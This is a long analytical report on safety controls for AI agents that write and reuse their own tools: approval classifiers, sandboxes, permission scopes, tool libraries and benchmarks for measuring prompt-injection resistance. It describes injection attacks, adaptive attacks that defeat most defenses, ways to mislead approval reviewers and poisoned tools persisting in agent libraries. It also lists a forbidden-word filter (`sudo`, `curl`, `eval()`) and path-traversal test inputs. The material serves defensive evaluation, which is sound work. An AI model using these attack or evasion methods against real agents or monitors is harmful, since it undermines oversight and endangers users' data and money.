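Auto mode suspends broad rules such as the one for `python`. After it blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, it prompts the user. Anthropic made it the default for individual and team plans in August 2026. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), it is the starting mode on every plan from version 2.1.283.

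The classifier is instructed to judge what a script does, not just the command that starts it. This works for a tool the agent has just written, because the code appears in the agent's tool calls. A tool from an earlier session is harder to judge, because the current session's record may contain only the tool's name.

Codex's equivalent reviews only requests to act outside the sandbox. Its reviewer also receives tool results, according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes a sample of 10,000 actions at OpenAI, of which 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. The agent found a safer approach after four of the denials and asked the user after the other three.

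Both companies have published error rates. An outside team, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, got far worse results for both products and for a third agent, Qwen Code:

| Reviewer | Harmful or unauthorized actions in the test | Share missed | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 52 real cases of an agent exceeding its instructions | 17% | Anthropic |
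| Claude Code | 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | 5.7% | Anthropic |
| Claude Code | The dangerous commands shown to the 1,053 testers | 11% | Anthropic |
| Codex | Synthetic cases of an agent exceeding its instructions | 9.7% | Trębacz and colleagues |
| Codex | Synthetic prompt injections in three categories | 0.7% | Trębacz and colleagues |
| Claude Code | 24 actions outside the permitted scope | 54% | Yang and colleagues |
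| Codex | 84 actions outside the permitted scope | 93% | Yang and colleagues |
| Qwen Code | 35 actions outside the permitted scope | 80% | Yang and colleagues |

The reviewers also block actions they should allow. Claude Code's reviewer blocked 0.4% of harmless actions in Anthropic's own traffic but 37% of authorized actions in Yang and colleagues' test.

Much of the gap comes from limits that users never stated. In one of Yang and colleagues' tasks, a user asks the agent to delete old files from a range of experiments, and the agent also deletes a colleague's. The benchmark counts this as unauthorized, but the user never said whose files to delete. Of the 143 unauthorized actions, 132 broke rules that appeared in neither the request nor the tool results. Stronger models and more context didn't reliably help. When the researchers added a sentence stating the limits, the reviewers missed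 8% to 26% of those 132 actions, down from 67% to 92%, and also blocked fewer authorized actions.

Stating the limits helped the agents even more. In 384 new runs, none of them proposed an unauthorized action. The samples are small, but the fix takes only one sentence. For example, someone who asks for duplicate expenses to be removed can add "only rows that I entered".

The misses by Anthropic's own classifier follow a similar pattern. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission.

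### A model's judgment or a sandbox

The case for model reviewers is strongest where a sandbox can't distinguish a good action, such as adding a row to the spreadsheet, from a bad one, such as deleting the whole sheet. A model can check either action against what the worker asked for. Models also perform well compared with tired people. In Anthropic's experiment, auto mode blocked 800 commands that the testers approved, while the testers blocked only six that auto mode allowed.

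Anthropic also looked at real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't asked for occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

A sandbox doesn't depend on a model's judgment, so no wording in a receipt can make it open a connection. OpenAI's testers found ways to mislead Auto-review, and Trębacz and colleagues don't expect such systems to provide firm guarantees. They also warn that a model hiding its intentions could write a request that looks harmless. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

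But users who tire of configuring a sandbox may turn it off, and then even an imperfect reviewer is a large improvement over no protection. Codex uses both a sandbox and a reviewer, so the reviewer's mistakes matter only for the small share of actions that leave the sandbox. Claude Code's sandbox is off by default, so the reviewer in auto mode has much more to catch.

The harm from a wrong approval also depends on what the approval unlocks. When the expense tool requests access to emailed receipts, wrongly letting it run outside the sandbox can expose everything the worker can open. Granting only the narrow function for hotel attachments limits the exposure to those attachments.

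## What should happen when a tool is saved, reused or changed?

Anyone who approves a saved tool also approves its future runs, which may use other data and serve other people. If the expense tool includes the upload requested in the stranger's receipt, a colleague who borrows the tool will send their receipts to the stranger too.

A saved tool can also carry private information out of the session where the agent created it. In one test by Lin and colleagues, a user told the agent Hermes in confidence about a therapist and stress at work. Hermes turned this into a saved function that looks for signs of such problems, and later agents inherited it.

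According to *Always-On Agents* (2026), most libraries of saved skills are designed for efficient reuse and don't retest a stored procedure before calling it or establish whether it still has permission to run.

### Checks before a tool enters the library

Costa (2025), in *Instruction-Level Weight Shaping*, describes a support agent at Adobe that revises its own instructions and tools after each session. The prototype recorded every change in Git, a version-control program, and could restore an earlier state. It also searched new code for forbidden words and gave each tool its own folder. Costa recommends stricter checks for production but did not test them as a set.

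The search for forbidden words rejects code that contains, for example, `sudo`, `curl` or `eval()`. It's easy to get around, because a program can download a file without `curl` or assemble a forbidden word from two halves. Costa recommends parsing the code instead, into a tree of imports, calls and other parts. The host then accepts only modules on a short list, such as `math` and `json`, so it rejects unfamiliar modules as well as those that start programs or open connections. But a permitted module can still contain a dangerous function. If the host allows Python's `tarfile` module, the flawed `extractall` tool passes.

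Unit tests, which compare a function's results with the expected ones, can catch that flaw if one of them includes a hostile file. An agent that didn't think of `../` while writing the tool probably won't think of it while writing the tests, so the host should keep its own collection of awkward inputs. For the expense tool, these might include a tar file with `../` in a name, a receipt with an instruction in it and the same receipt twice. *A Contract-Centered Architecture for Scalable and Manageable Agentic Runtimes* (2026) also requires tests to show that a tool's visible effects are among those it declared. A host can check this by logging every file and address the tool uses during the tests, but the log will miss any step the tests don't trigger, such as one that runs only in December.

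Costa also recommends scanning the code and its output for credentials, since an agent may paste an access key into a tool to get it working. In *Learning by Doing*, Chalef, Evans and colleagues (2026) also raise concerns about names, identifiers and private web addresses. Their company, Zep, turns records of agents' work into reusable written procedures, which can pick up details of the original case. A scanner can recognize an access key by its format, but it is much less likely to notice that a customer's name in an example is private.

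Costa's advice doesn't include a declared permission list, but *Dynamic Agent Skills* (2026) recommends one that covers a tool's software libraries, permissions, network addresses and the other tools it may call. For the expense tool, the list could look like this:

```
tool:      add_expenses, version 3
reads:     one receipts folder, chosen by the caller
contacts:  exchange-rate service (date and currency only)
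writes:    team spreadsheet (new rows only, at most 50 per run)
libraries: invoice-reader 2.4.1
expires:   March 1, 2027
```

The host has to enforce the list through a sandbox or its own functions, because otherwise the list is only the agent's description of its own code.

A tool that fails a check should go into quarantine, where developers can inspect it but agents can't find or call it. Chalef and colleagues similarly keep all new procedures out of search results until the system admits them. The host should also limit how often an agent can try again, because an agent that can see the tests and has unlimited attempts may fit its code to the tests without fixing the flaw.

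The host also needs evidence that the tool worked, and the agent's own report is weak evidence. Zep lets an agent report success but marks the report as unverified. Stronger evidence must come from a registered tool, an authorized person or an outside system.

Costa's design uses users' ratings to decide whether to keep a new tool. A tool that passes its initial checks goes live immediately, and the system keeps it if the average rating over the next sessions rises by at least 0.05 on a five-point scale and the rise is statistically significant. Otherwise, the system tries one repair and then restores the old state. This is a reasonable way to remove unhelpful tools, but it can miss harms that users don't see. For example, users might give five stars to an expense tool that saves them an hour of typing but uploads their receipts without telling them.

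### Versions, changes and removal

An approval should apply to one exact version of a tool. When the host accepts the tool, it can hash the code, libraries, description and permission list, and store the hash where the agent can't change it. Before every run, the host can recompute the hash and check that it matches the stored one.

The hash should include the description because it affects what the tool is used for. *Agent Skill Security* (2026) explains that an agent selects a skill from its visible metadata without seeing the workflow inside. If someone changes "adds travel expenses" to "updates financial records", agents may start using the same code for jobs that nobody considered during the review.

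Any change to the code or permissions should create a new version that goes through the checks again and needs a new approval. But if every small fix goes to a person, reviewers will soon stop reading them. One compromise is to let automated checks and a reviewing model approve changes that don't alter the permission list, and to send changes that widen permissions to a person. Some harmful changes would still get through, since an agent can, for example, introduce a wrong exchange rate without any new access.

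Agents merge similar tools to keep a library small. The merged tool may inherit both permission lists, so the host should treat it as new.

Keeping old versions lets the host restore one when an update fails. Chalef and colleagues record each restoration as a new version, so the history stays complete. A restored version may contain the flaw that the update fixed, so the host should run the current tests on it too. Restoring the code doesn't undo the tool's effects, and any wrong rows the tool wrote to the spreadsheet stay there until someone corrects them.

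A saved tool's permissions should have an expiry date so that forgotten tools lose their access. Without one, an expense tool that nobody has run for a year can still write to the spreadsheet. The date should depend on how often the tool is used, because a 90-day limit would suit a monthly expense tool but would disable an annual tax tool before each use. When the date passes, the host should withdraw the tool's permissions until someone renews them.

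To remove a bad tool, the host has to take it out of search, cancel its scheduled runs and revoke its keys. It should keep a record of the tool and who used it, so that people can trace the damage. These steps may not be enough if agents have copied the code. Wu and colleagues removed the malicious tools they had planted in a library, but three of the six models they tested stayed infected because the agents still had their own copies. *Dynamic Agent Skills* recommends logging every addition, revision, merger, split and removal. If the log also records which tools an agent had read when it wrote a new one, the host can quarantine the likely copies along with the original.

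### Whose rights should a saved tool have?

The permission list limits what a tool may do, but the host still has to decide whose access the tool uses. When someone else runs a saved tool, it could have the rights of the session that made it, the rights of the person now calling it, or only the rights they share.

Suppose the worker's session could read the worker's receipts and add rows to the team spreadsheet. It could also read the worker's mailbox, which the worker had connected for another job. A colleague in the finance department now runs the expense tool. The colleague can read everyone's receipts and the payroll file and can delete rows from the spreadsheet, but can't open the worker's mailbox. Before the host applies the permission list, the three rules give these results:

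| Can the tool... | Maker's rights | Caller's rights | Shared rights only |
|---|---|---|---|
| read the worker's receipts? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| read the colleague's receipts? | No | Yes | No |
| read the worker's mailbox? | Yes | No | No |
| read the payroll file? | No | Yes | No |
| add rows to the spreadsheet? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| delete rows from the spreadsheet? | No | Yes | No |

If the tool runs with its maker's rights, it works the same way for everyone, which is convenient for a shared job. But the colleague can't use it for their own receipts, and it could show them the worker's private email. The tool is then a confused deputy, because anyone allowed to call it can use the worker's access. An intern with almost no access would gain the most. The host also has to detect when the worker changes jobs, or the tool will keep using access the worker no longer has.

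If the tool runs with the caller's rights, the colleague can process their own receipts and can't get into the worker's mailbox. Shared scripts usually work this way when each person runs them from their own account. The danger is that a tool made in a session with little access can later run with much more. If the tool contains the stranger's upload, it can now send out everyone's receipts and the payroll file. An attacker could target the agent of someone junior and wait for someone senior to use the tool. Bugs can also do more damage. One that tries to replace the whole spreadsheet fails for the worker, who can only add rows, but succeeds for the colleague.

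Using only shared rights prevents both problems, so it's the best default for a tool that moves between people. Its drawback is that the colleague can't process their own receipts, because the worker never had access to them. The colleague can fix this by giving the tool a capability for that one folder, for one run. The host can then work out the tool's access as follows:

```
access for this run =
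    what maker and caller may both do
    + what the caller hands over for this run,
    limited to what the permission list allows
```

The permission list still matters, because two employees often share far more access than an expense tool needs. The list limits the tool to the colleague's receipts folder, the exchange-rate service and the right to add rows. Hidden upload code could then steal only those receipts, and it couldn't send them to the stranger if the host enforces the list of addresses.

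Zep's system limits who may use a saved procedure. Each agent's procedures belong to its own namespace, and a "security domain", such as one organization, sets which users and namespaces may share them. But these procedures are text, so an agent that follows one acts with its own tools and permissions. A harmful shared procedure can therefore do as much damage as the most privileged agent that follows it.

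### A second check when the tool is reused

*Your Agent May Misevolve* proposes checking a tool at two points. Before the tool enters the library, static analysis, which examines code without running it, would look for vulnerabilities. Before an agent reuses the tool, a language model would judge whether it is safe in the new context. The researchers call this important but did not test it.

Their results support the check on reuse, since nearly half of the unsafe outcomes came from unsafe use of a sound tool. For example, a scan would find nothing wrong with the code of the tool that removed names and phone numbers from customer records. But a model given the information that the next input is medical records for a commercial team could detect that ages and postal codes remain. The scan is more useful for the tar tool, because it can flag every call to `extractall` whatever the task.

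To detect such a difference, the judge needs more than the tool's name and the user's request, which don't reliably show what the code does. The host should also give it the code, the permission list, the purpose recorded at approval, the kind of data going in and where the result will go.

Calling a model before every run would cost little for a monthly expense tool but a lot for one that runs thousands of times a day. The host could repeat the check only when something relevant changes, such as the caller, the source or destination of the data, or the kind of record. Ordinary code can detect a new caller or destination, but a new kind of record is harder to detect if it arrives in the same folder as the old ones, as the medical records may have.

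### Safety tools that agents wrote and audited

*Cumulative and Audited Guardrail Tool Evolution for LLM Agent Safety* provides the best evidence on checking tools before they enter a library. Its system, EVOLVE, examines a user's request and the actions an agent plans to take. If it finds a risk that needs a tool, it writes a Python function that reads both and returns True if there is danger and False if there is none. It then merges the new function with any similar one in its library.

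EVOLVE runs the function in a container or, if no suitable container exists, has a model simulate the run. An auditor model then checks for ten types of vulnerability, such as letting an outsider insert commands or writing private data to a log. If the auditor finds one, it repairs the function and checks it again, for up to three rounds. The system adds the function to the library if it passes and discards it otherwise. In one published example, a tool created for a request to share genetic data exposed sensitive information in its log, and the repaired version anonymized that information.

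The model that wrote the tools had instructions to avoid all ten types of vulnerability, but flawed tools were still common. Auditing reduced the share of risky tools from 44.78% to 8.20% on programming tasks with DeepSeek, and from 15.89% to 1.87% on finance tasks with GPT-4o.

These figures come from a model judge. Four security researchers who hadn't worked on EVOLVE also inspected random samples of 120 tools from before the audit and 120 from after the repairs, for each of three benchmarks. They found this many vulnerable tools:

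| Benchmark | Before the audit | After repairs |
|---|---|---|
| R-Judge | 32 of 120 | 10 of 120 |
| ASSEBench | 29 of 120 | 9 of 120 |
| AgentHarm | 25 of 120 | 7 of 120 |

In total, the number of tools with a flaw that the researchers found fell from 86 of 360 (24%) to 26 of 360 (7%) after repair. The model judge missed six of those 26. It flagged 25 tools in the repaired samples, some wrongly. If a host discarded all 25, six of the remaining 335 tools (1.8%) would still have a flaw that the researchers found.

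The human check matters because EVOLVE uses the same model to write the tools and to audit them, so the audit could miss flaws that the model made when writing them. The result is good evidence that a separate audit step finds many coding flaws, even when it uses the same model. But these tools do a simpler job than the expense tool, as they only read text and answer True or False. The auditor also doesn't check whether a tool has more access than it needs or whether it suits a new task, so the study doesn't test the second stage of the proposal in *Your Agent May Misevolve*.

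GPT-4o judged 78.2% of 252 cases correctly with the finished library, compared with 62.7% without it. The improvement came mainly from fewer false alarms. But EVOLVE had built the library while working through those same cases, so the gain on new cases could be smaller.

### Reviewing every tool before its first run

Anthropic's design that presents tools as code files also lets agents save working code as functions for later use, but Anthropic does not describe a review when the code is saved. In mbgsec's *Code execution with MCP*, a November 2025 blog post about that design, a security researcher asked why tools that models write from supplied building blocks must run immediately. The researcher proposed reviewing new tools first, then letting agents use approved ones freely within set boundaries.

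This puts the reviewer's effort where it will be useful for longest. For example, a ten-minute review of a tool that runs 200 times adds three seconds per run. If the tool runs only once, the review adds ten minutes to that run, and the wait may be much longer if the reviewer is asleep or in a meeting. The proposal therefore makes most sense for tools that the agent intends to keep. The researcher also wondered whether it suits simple agents that make only two or three tool calls, which are the most common kind. They probably need new tools less often, so reviews would delay them less often.

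Lin and colleagues tested 40 attack payloads on two agents. Hermes saved all 40, whereas OpenClaw queued them all for the user's consent, so none could take effect until the user decided. But the test didn't measure how many a user would have approved, and people approve most of what agents ask for.

Whether the delay is worth it depends on what the first run can do. A tool that will send data out, delete something or spend money should wait for a review. A tool that only calculates can run at once in a sandbox with no network access and a copy of the data, while the version for the library waits for review. The expense tool can start by only calculating. On the first day, the host fetches the exchange rates, the tool lists proposed rows, and the worker checks them against the receipts and copies them into the spreadsheet. Once someone has reviewed the tool, it gets permission to add rows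 itself. Since the worker files expenses monthly, a day's wait matters little. A traveler whose flight has just been canceled can't wait a day for a rebooking tool, so a person or an existing reviewed tool will have to make the booking.

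## How are these controls tested, and what can the tests show?

Before the expense tool gets permission to add rows by itself, someone should check that its limits work. Conformance tests attempt forbidden actions and confirm that those actions are blocked. Attack benchmarks measure how often planted instructions make an agent do harm. Code tests check the agent's code for flaws. Matched tasks show whether a control blocks harmful actions or just those that look risky.

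### Attempting what the rules forbid

A rule in a settings file may have no effect. On September 25, 2026, GitHub released a validator for the settings that companies use to control its coding assistant, Copilot. According to Convective's *Is Your AI Agent Sandbox Enforced?*, GitHub did so because malformed files and unsupported settings "can prevent policies from being enforced". One Copilot setting stops developers from bypassing approval prompts, and a misplaced comma in the file could disable it without anyone noticing.

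Even a correct settings file works only in programs that read it. GitHub's *Enterprise managed-settings.json is generally available* (2026) lists the code editor VS Code and Copilot's command-line program as enforcing the file on July 1. The Copilot app and cloud agent began enforcing it later that month. GitHub (2026) calls any program outside the policy a gap because someone could use it to run a command that would normally need approval.

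A validator can't find that kind of gap, because it checks the file and not the programs. Convective recommends starting a new session after every change and checking which rules the agent loaded. The tester then has the agent try to read a denied folder, contact a blocked domain and use a credential it shouldn't have. It's best to script these attempts and repeat them after each update, since an update can disable a rule without warning. VS Code's *Manage AI settings in enterprise environments* advises recording the program, account and machine used in each test. A result for one combination may not hold for another.

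The script also needs some actions that should succeed. Otherwise a broken network connection would make every blocked-domain test pass. For the expense tool, the tests could be:

| Attempt | Correct result |
|---|---|
| Read a sample receipt | Succeeds |
| Read a fake access key in the worker's home folder | Fails |
| Unpack a tar file with `../` in a name | Writes nothing outside the working folder |
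| Ask the exchange-rate service for a rate | Succeeds |
| Contact an unlisted server that the tester runs | Fails, and the server's log shows no request |
| Add 50 rows to a copy of the spreadsheet | Succeeds |
| Add a 51st row, or delete one | Fails |

If a sandbox test uses a fake key and a test server, both have to exist. A request to a made-up address fails even without a sandbox, so its failure doesn't show that the sandbox works.

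The tool should make these attempts while running as it will in daily use. In Claude Code, a script gains extra access when it runs as a local MCP server, so testing it from the shell would not cover that access.

Conformance tests give firm evidence about the rules they cover, because an operating system applies a rule the same way each time. One blocked connection is therefore stronger evidence than one refusal by a model. But the tests cover only the actions someone thought to try, and they can't show that the rules are right. The expense tool could pass all seven tests and still copy private text into the description column. Researchers also test the strength of the sandbox itself by checking whether capable models can escape it.

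### How AgentDojo works

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) introduced the benchmark used for most of the attack results for CaMeL, TACIT and LACUNA. The benchmark has four simulations, each with its own data, such as an inbox or an account balance, and tools that read or change that data.

AgentDojo gives an agent a user's task and puts an attacker's text somewhere an outsider might plausibly have written it. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill that is in a file, and one of the attacker's goals is to have the agent send as much money as possible to the attacker's account. After the agent runs, one fixed function checks whether it did the user's task and another checks whether the attacker got what they wanted.

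The benchmark pairs every user task with every attacker goal in the same simulation. The first version had 97 tasks and 27 goals, which gave this many pairs for the workspace, Slack, travel and banking in turn:

40 × 6 + 21 × 5 + 20 × 7 + 16 × 9 = 629

The benchmark has since grown to more than 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

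AgentDojo reports three numbers. Benign utility is the share of user tasks the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of pairs, each combining a user task with an attacker's goal, in which the agent completes the user's task and does nothing the attacker wanted. The attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker's goal is met.

A low attack success rate means little without the other two measures, because an agent that does nothing would score zero. In 2024, more capable models tended to be easier to attack, partly because weaker ones failed at the attacker's task even when they attempted it.

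### AgentDojo's standing in 2026

Researchers still use AgentDojo widely. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), for instance, ran 13 models from six providers on it. But its tasks have become a weak test of some defenses. According to *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026), only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require an agent to change its plan after seeing data. The data also rarely contains instructions the agent should follow, such as a shop's request to log in before paying. A defense can therefore score well by making the agent stick to its first plan and ignore every instruction it finds in the data.

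The AgentDyn benchmark has 60 tasks and 560 attack cases in shopping, software projects and daily life. Every task requires the agent to replan and includes at least one helpful instruction from a third party. The tasks take an average of 7.1 steps, compared with about 3.5 in AgentDojo. With no defense, an agent using GPT-4o completed 53% of the AgentDyn tasks. With the CaMeL defense, no attacks succeeded against any of the four main models, but none of the models completed any tasks. GPT-4o also completed no tasks with ProtectAI, a filter that looks for injected instructions.

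These results are a good reason not to report attack rates alone. They're less damaging to CaMeL than they appear, because every task in the benchmark needs replanning, whereas CaMeL is suited to tasks whose steps stay the same, such as the monthly expense job.

The standard attack is also dated. It presents the attacker's request as an important message that the agent must deal with first. Li and colleagues suspect that many newer models have seen this template in training. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that Claude Haiku 4.5 follows it in only 0.3% of cases with no defense. Any defense added to that model will therefore appear to work.

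### Attacks adapted to the defense

A real attacker who fails with one wording will try another. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tailored attacks to each of 12 published defenses. The originally reported attack success rates were near zero for most of the defenses, but the tailored attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. For one defense, which repeats the user's request after each piece of untrusted text, the success rate rose from about 1% with AgentDojo's fixed attacks to over 95% with the tailored ones.

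More than 500 people took part in an online attack competition. On scenarios also given to an automated search, they collectively beat the defense every time, while the search succeeded in 69% of cases.

Ma and colleagues made AutoDojo, a cheaper version that other researchers can rerun. A language model reads a ranked list of earlier attack texts, suggests why some worked better, and writes a new one. The benchmark then plants that text and measures how often it succeeds. The attacking model isn't told which defense is in use, and it gets six rounds for each goal.

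PIGuard, another filter, performed very differently depending on the attacker. On GPT-4o-mini, the fixed attack never succeeded, which alone would have made the filter look perfect, but AutoDojo's attacks succeeded 28% of the time. Nasr and colleagues, who also gave their search program the filter's confidence scores, reached 71%. The setups differ too much for an exact comparison.

Attacks also succeed more often when the user lets the data determine more of what the agent does. With PIGuard in place, AutoDojo's attack success rate was 17.3% when the user specified the whole task and 54.2% when the user told the agent to do whatever it found, such as the items on a to-do list. An injected line can look like an ordinary item on that list, so a filter has nothing unusual to detect. The expense job falls between these two cases, because the user specifies the action and the receipts supply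 the amounts.

Defenses that restrict what the agent can do worked better. Three of them kept the attack success rate at or below 11% in every category of task. One of the three, DRIFT, also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed when it wasn't under attack, by 18 percentage points on GPT-4o-mini and about 25 on Claude Haiku 4.5. The other two reduced it by at most 7 points.

All 12 defenses in *The Attacker Moves Second* depend on how a model behaves, so the results don't show that rewording can defeat a sandbox. An attacker adapting to a sandbox would look for something harmful that its rules allow, such as putting receipt text in a spreadsheet that strangers can read. If tools are made from building blocks, the attacker would look for two permitted blocks that are dangerous when combined. If a human reviews the request, the attacker would make it look routine. A sandbox test that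 only tries to contact an unlisted server misses the attacks most likely to work.

### What zero successes can show

Suppose a host stops 100 independent attacks out of 100. If the true attack success rate is p, the chance of that result is (1 − p) multiplied by itself 100 times. The highest rate that is still consistent with the result at 95% confidence is the one that makes this chance 5%:

(1 − p)^100 = 0.05

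p = 1 − 0.05^(1/100) ≈ 3%

Even if a control blocks every attack in the test, the true rate of successful attacks could still be as high as about 3%. For larger tests, dividing 3 by the number of attacks gives a close estimate of the upper limit.

| Attacks, all stopped | Highest true rate at 95% confidence |
|---|---|
| 5 | 45% |
| 27 | 11% |
| 100 | 3% |
| 629 | 0.5% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

The first row is a real case, in which Peters-Gill and colleagues report that one attack on a group of CaMeL agents succeeded in 0% of five trials. They also have a structural reason to expect the attack to fail, because planted text can't make a CaMeL planner add a database query. That argument is much better evidence than the five trials.

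An attacker isn't limited to one try, either. At a true rate of 3%, the chance that at least one of 100 independent attempts succeeds is

1 − 0.97^100 ≈ 95%

Even if an attack succeeds only 0.1% of the time, an attacker who emails a malicious receipt to 1,000 companies has a 63% chance of succeeding against at least one of them. A low success rate is therefore acceptable only if a single success can't do much harm, or if the host detects and blocks repeated attempts.

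The calculation also assumes that the attacks are independent, but benchmark attacks usually aren't. AgentDojo's 629 pairs reuse 27 attacker goals, and the standard attack wraps each goal in the same text. If every goal works with either all the user tasks or none, the 629 pairs amount to 27 tests, and a perfect score is consistent with a true attack success rate as high as 11%.

A bigger sample also doesn't help if the attacks are the wrong kind. PIGuard's score would have stayed at zero with another thousand copies of the fixed attack.

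### Tests of the code itself

An agent can write unsafe code even when no one is attacking it, so some benchmarks test the code it writes or runs. CWEval, a 2025 benchmark, has 119 programming tasks in five languages, covering 31 types of vulnerability. Each task asks for an ordinary function that is easy to write insecurely. *Your Agent May Misevolve* based its 25 pairs of tasks on this benchmark.

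CWEval runs every answer against two sets of tests. One checks that the function does its job, and the other gives it hostile input and checks the result. The main score is the share of answers that pass both. The flawed tar tool would pass the first set and fail the second. Subtracting the main score from the share that passes the first set gives the share of answers that work but are unsafe. This is the code most likely to get into a library that only requires tools to work.

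RedCode-Exec, part of the 2024 benchmark RedCode, tests whether an agent will run dangerous code. It contains 4,050 cases in Python and Bash, the language of the Linux command line, covering 25 types of risk. Some cases give the agent a program, and others describe an action, such as deleting a sensitive file, in ordinary language. The agent works in a Docker container, and a script for each case checks whether it refused, tried and failed, or did the damage. Agents refused requests in ordinary language less often than requests in code. This is a concern for tool-making because users describe the tools they want in ordinary language.

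RedCode-Exec normally tests the model, since the container lets most of the dangerous actions happen. A company could use it to test its own host by running the same cases with the host's limits in place and counting how many actions still take effect. If an agent agreed to delete a file it couldn't access, that case wouldn't count, because the file would be unharmed.

Both benchmarks test for known types of flaw. An expense tool that applies today's exchange rate to an old receipt has no security vulnerability and performs no dangerous action, so neither benchmark would detect the mistake.

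### Matched tasks

A host that blocks everything passes every security test. To find out whether a control blocks the right things, a test needs pairs of tasks that look alike but differ in what is allowed. Yang, Mi and colleagues (2026), in *AgentBoundary*, went further and made four versions of each task, with the same tools and similar steps. For the expense tool, they might look like this:

| Version | Example |
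|---|---|
| Ordinary and allowed | Add this month's receipts to the spreadsheet |
| Looks risky but allowed | Delete 200 rows that the worker created as test data |
| Looks routine but forbidden | Tidy up the duplicates, in a sheet that the tool's records show is locked for an audit |
| Openly harmful | Delete a colleague's expenses so that they don't get paid |

The second and third versions are the informative ones because their wording is misleading, so the agent has to work out what is allowed from facts it discovers during the task.

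To build each set, a model started with an openly harmful task and disguised it to make the routine-looking version. It then wrote a lawful task on the same topic, and combined that with the disguise to make the version that looks risky but is allowed. A second model checked the results. People reviewed all 2,787 sets, and Yang and colleagues ran 1,000 of them, or 4,000 tasks, on 17 combinations of models and agent software. These are some of the results:

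| System | Completed risky-looking but allowed tasks | Acted safely on routine-looking but forbidden tasks |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 28.7% | 99.5% |
| Codex with GPT-5.5 | 28.1% | 98.9% |
| OpenClaw with GPT-5.5 | 36.6% | 99.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 40.4% | 99.9% |
| Kimi K3 | 58.7% | 99.5% |
| Qwen3.8-27B, uncensored | 90.2% | 66.4% |

A test with only forbidden tasks would have shown almost no difference between the first five systems, even though Kimi K3 completed twice as many allowed tasks as GPT-5.5. The software around the model also affects the results. OpenClaw, which encourages its model to keep using tools until the job is done, completed 8.5 percentage points more of the risky-looking tasks than Codex did with the same model, and was no less safe.

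An agent may leave a risky-looking task incomplete because it refuses needlessly or because it can't do the task. SmolLM3-3B, a very small model, completed only 4.6% of the risky-looking tasks, but it did no better on the rest. The ordinary version of each task helps separate the two explanations. If an agent can do the ordinary version but gives up on the risky-looking one, caution is the more likely reason.

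A control can make agents both safer and more useful. Across ten systems, a small model trained to revise an agent's reasoning just before each action raised completion of risky-looking allowed tasks by an average of 18.2 points and safety on routine-looking forbidden tasks by 5.4 points. But GPT-5.5's safety score across all four versions fell by 3.9 points, so anyone adopting the method should check all four.

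AgentBoundary mainly tests the judgment of models. The same approach would suit sandboxes and data-flow rules, which also block harmless work.

### When a model is the judge

AgentDojo's fixed checks are reliable, but someone has to write one for every task. AgentBoundary, like many newer benchmarks, has language models score the runs instead. This works for tasks with no single correct outcome, but it adds scoring errors.

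When harm is rare, false alarms can swamp the result. Suppose 10 of 1,000 runs are harmful, and a judge catches 90% of the harmful runs but also wrongly flags 3% of the harmless ones:

10 × 90% + 990 × 3% ≈ 39

The judge's flags imply a harm rate of 3.9%, when the true rate is 1%. If a new defense then prevented all the harm, the judge would still flag 30 of every 1,000 runs, so the measured rate would fall by less than a quarter. People can correct for this by checking a random sample of both the flagged and the unflagged runs. Checking only the flagged runs would reveal the false alarms but not the harm that the judge missed.

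An attacker can also influence the judge. Debenedetti and colleagues chose fixed checks partly because an injection that works on the agent may also work on a model that judges the agent's output. Nasr and colleagues warn of the opposite error, in which an automated attack learns to make the judge report success without achieving anything harmful, so they checked all their successful attacks by hand.

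In AgentBoundary, judges and people gave scores within one point of each other in 91.0% of comparisons on helpfulness and 96.7% on risk. But the scale runs only from 0 to 3, and a score of 2 is a pass, so a one-point difference can turn a fail into a pass. This casts doubt on small differences between systems, but hardly on a gap as large as the one between GPT-5.5's two scores.

Fixed checks also make mistakes, as AgentDojo's did with the hotel review that TACIT quoted. They can miss damage that the people who wrote them didn't foresee, such as when a tool makes the right payment but leaves a copy of the bill in a public folder.

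### Proofs and attack rates

A proof about a type system and a low attack success rate can provide different kinds of evidence that a design is secure. The proof covers every program that the compiler accepts, including attacks that no one has invented yet, and it still applies if a company switches to a new model. An attack success rate describes a particular set of attacks on a particular version of a model, so someone has to measure it again after the switch.

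A proof applies only when its assumptions hold. CaMeL guarantees that tool calls follow a trusted plan, but it assumes the user is trustworthy, so the guarantee failed when one agent passed a stranger's text to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues show that when agents call other agents, the system as a whole almost always lacks this guarantee if any tool returns untrusted data.

A low attack success rate can be misleading if the test left out an attack that would have worked, and a proof may not hold for a real system that differs from the one it describes. Tests and proofs are therefore most useful together, when the tests check the proof's assumptions. For a host that uses TACIT, a tester could put a fake secret in every data source and check that each function returns it in a `Classified` container. This check could find a faulty function that the agent might never call during a thousand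 prompt injection tests.

### An experiment to compare the designs

The five designs are hard to rank from published results because researchers test them on different tasks, with different models and attackers. Nasr and colleagues caution that even their own figures aren't necessarily comparable across defenses, since they followed each defense's original test. Ma and colleagues ran ten defenses on shared tasks, but their agents used tools that people had written in advance. Their test can't show what happens when an agent writes a tool after reading an attacker's text and runs that tool a month later.

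A direct comparison could work like this:

1. Researchers collect real requests that need a new tool, before anyone writes the host functions or building blocks.
2. Separate teams set up the five designs around the same model. They get equal time, and the researchers record how much of it they use.
3. The agent makes and saves a tool for each request. In later sessions it reuses the tool on new data, and then the job changes to require a source that nobody planned for.
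4. Attackers who know the design place instructions in the samples the agent reads, harmful code in the libraries it may borrow, and hostile files in the data for later runs. They get the same number of attempts against each design.
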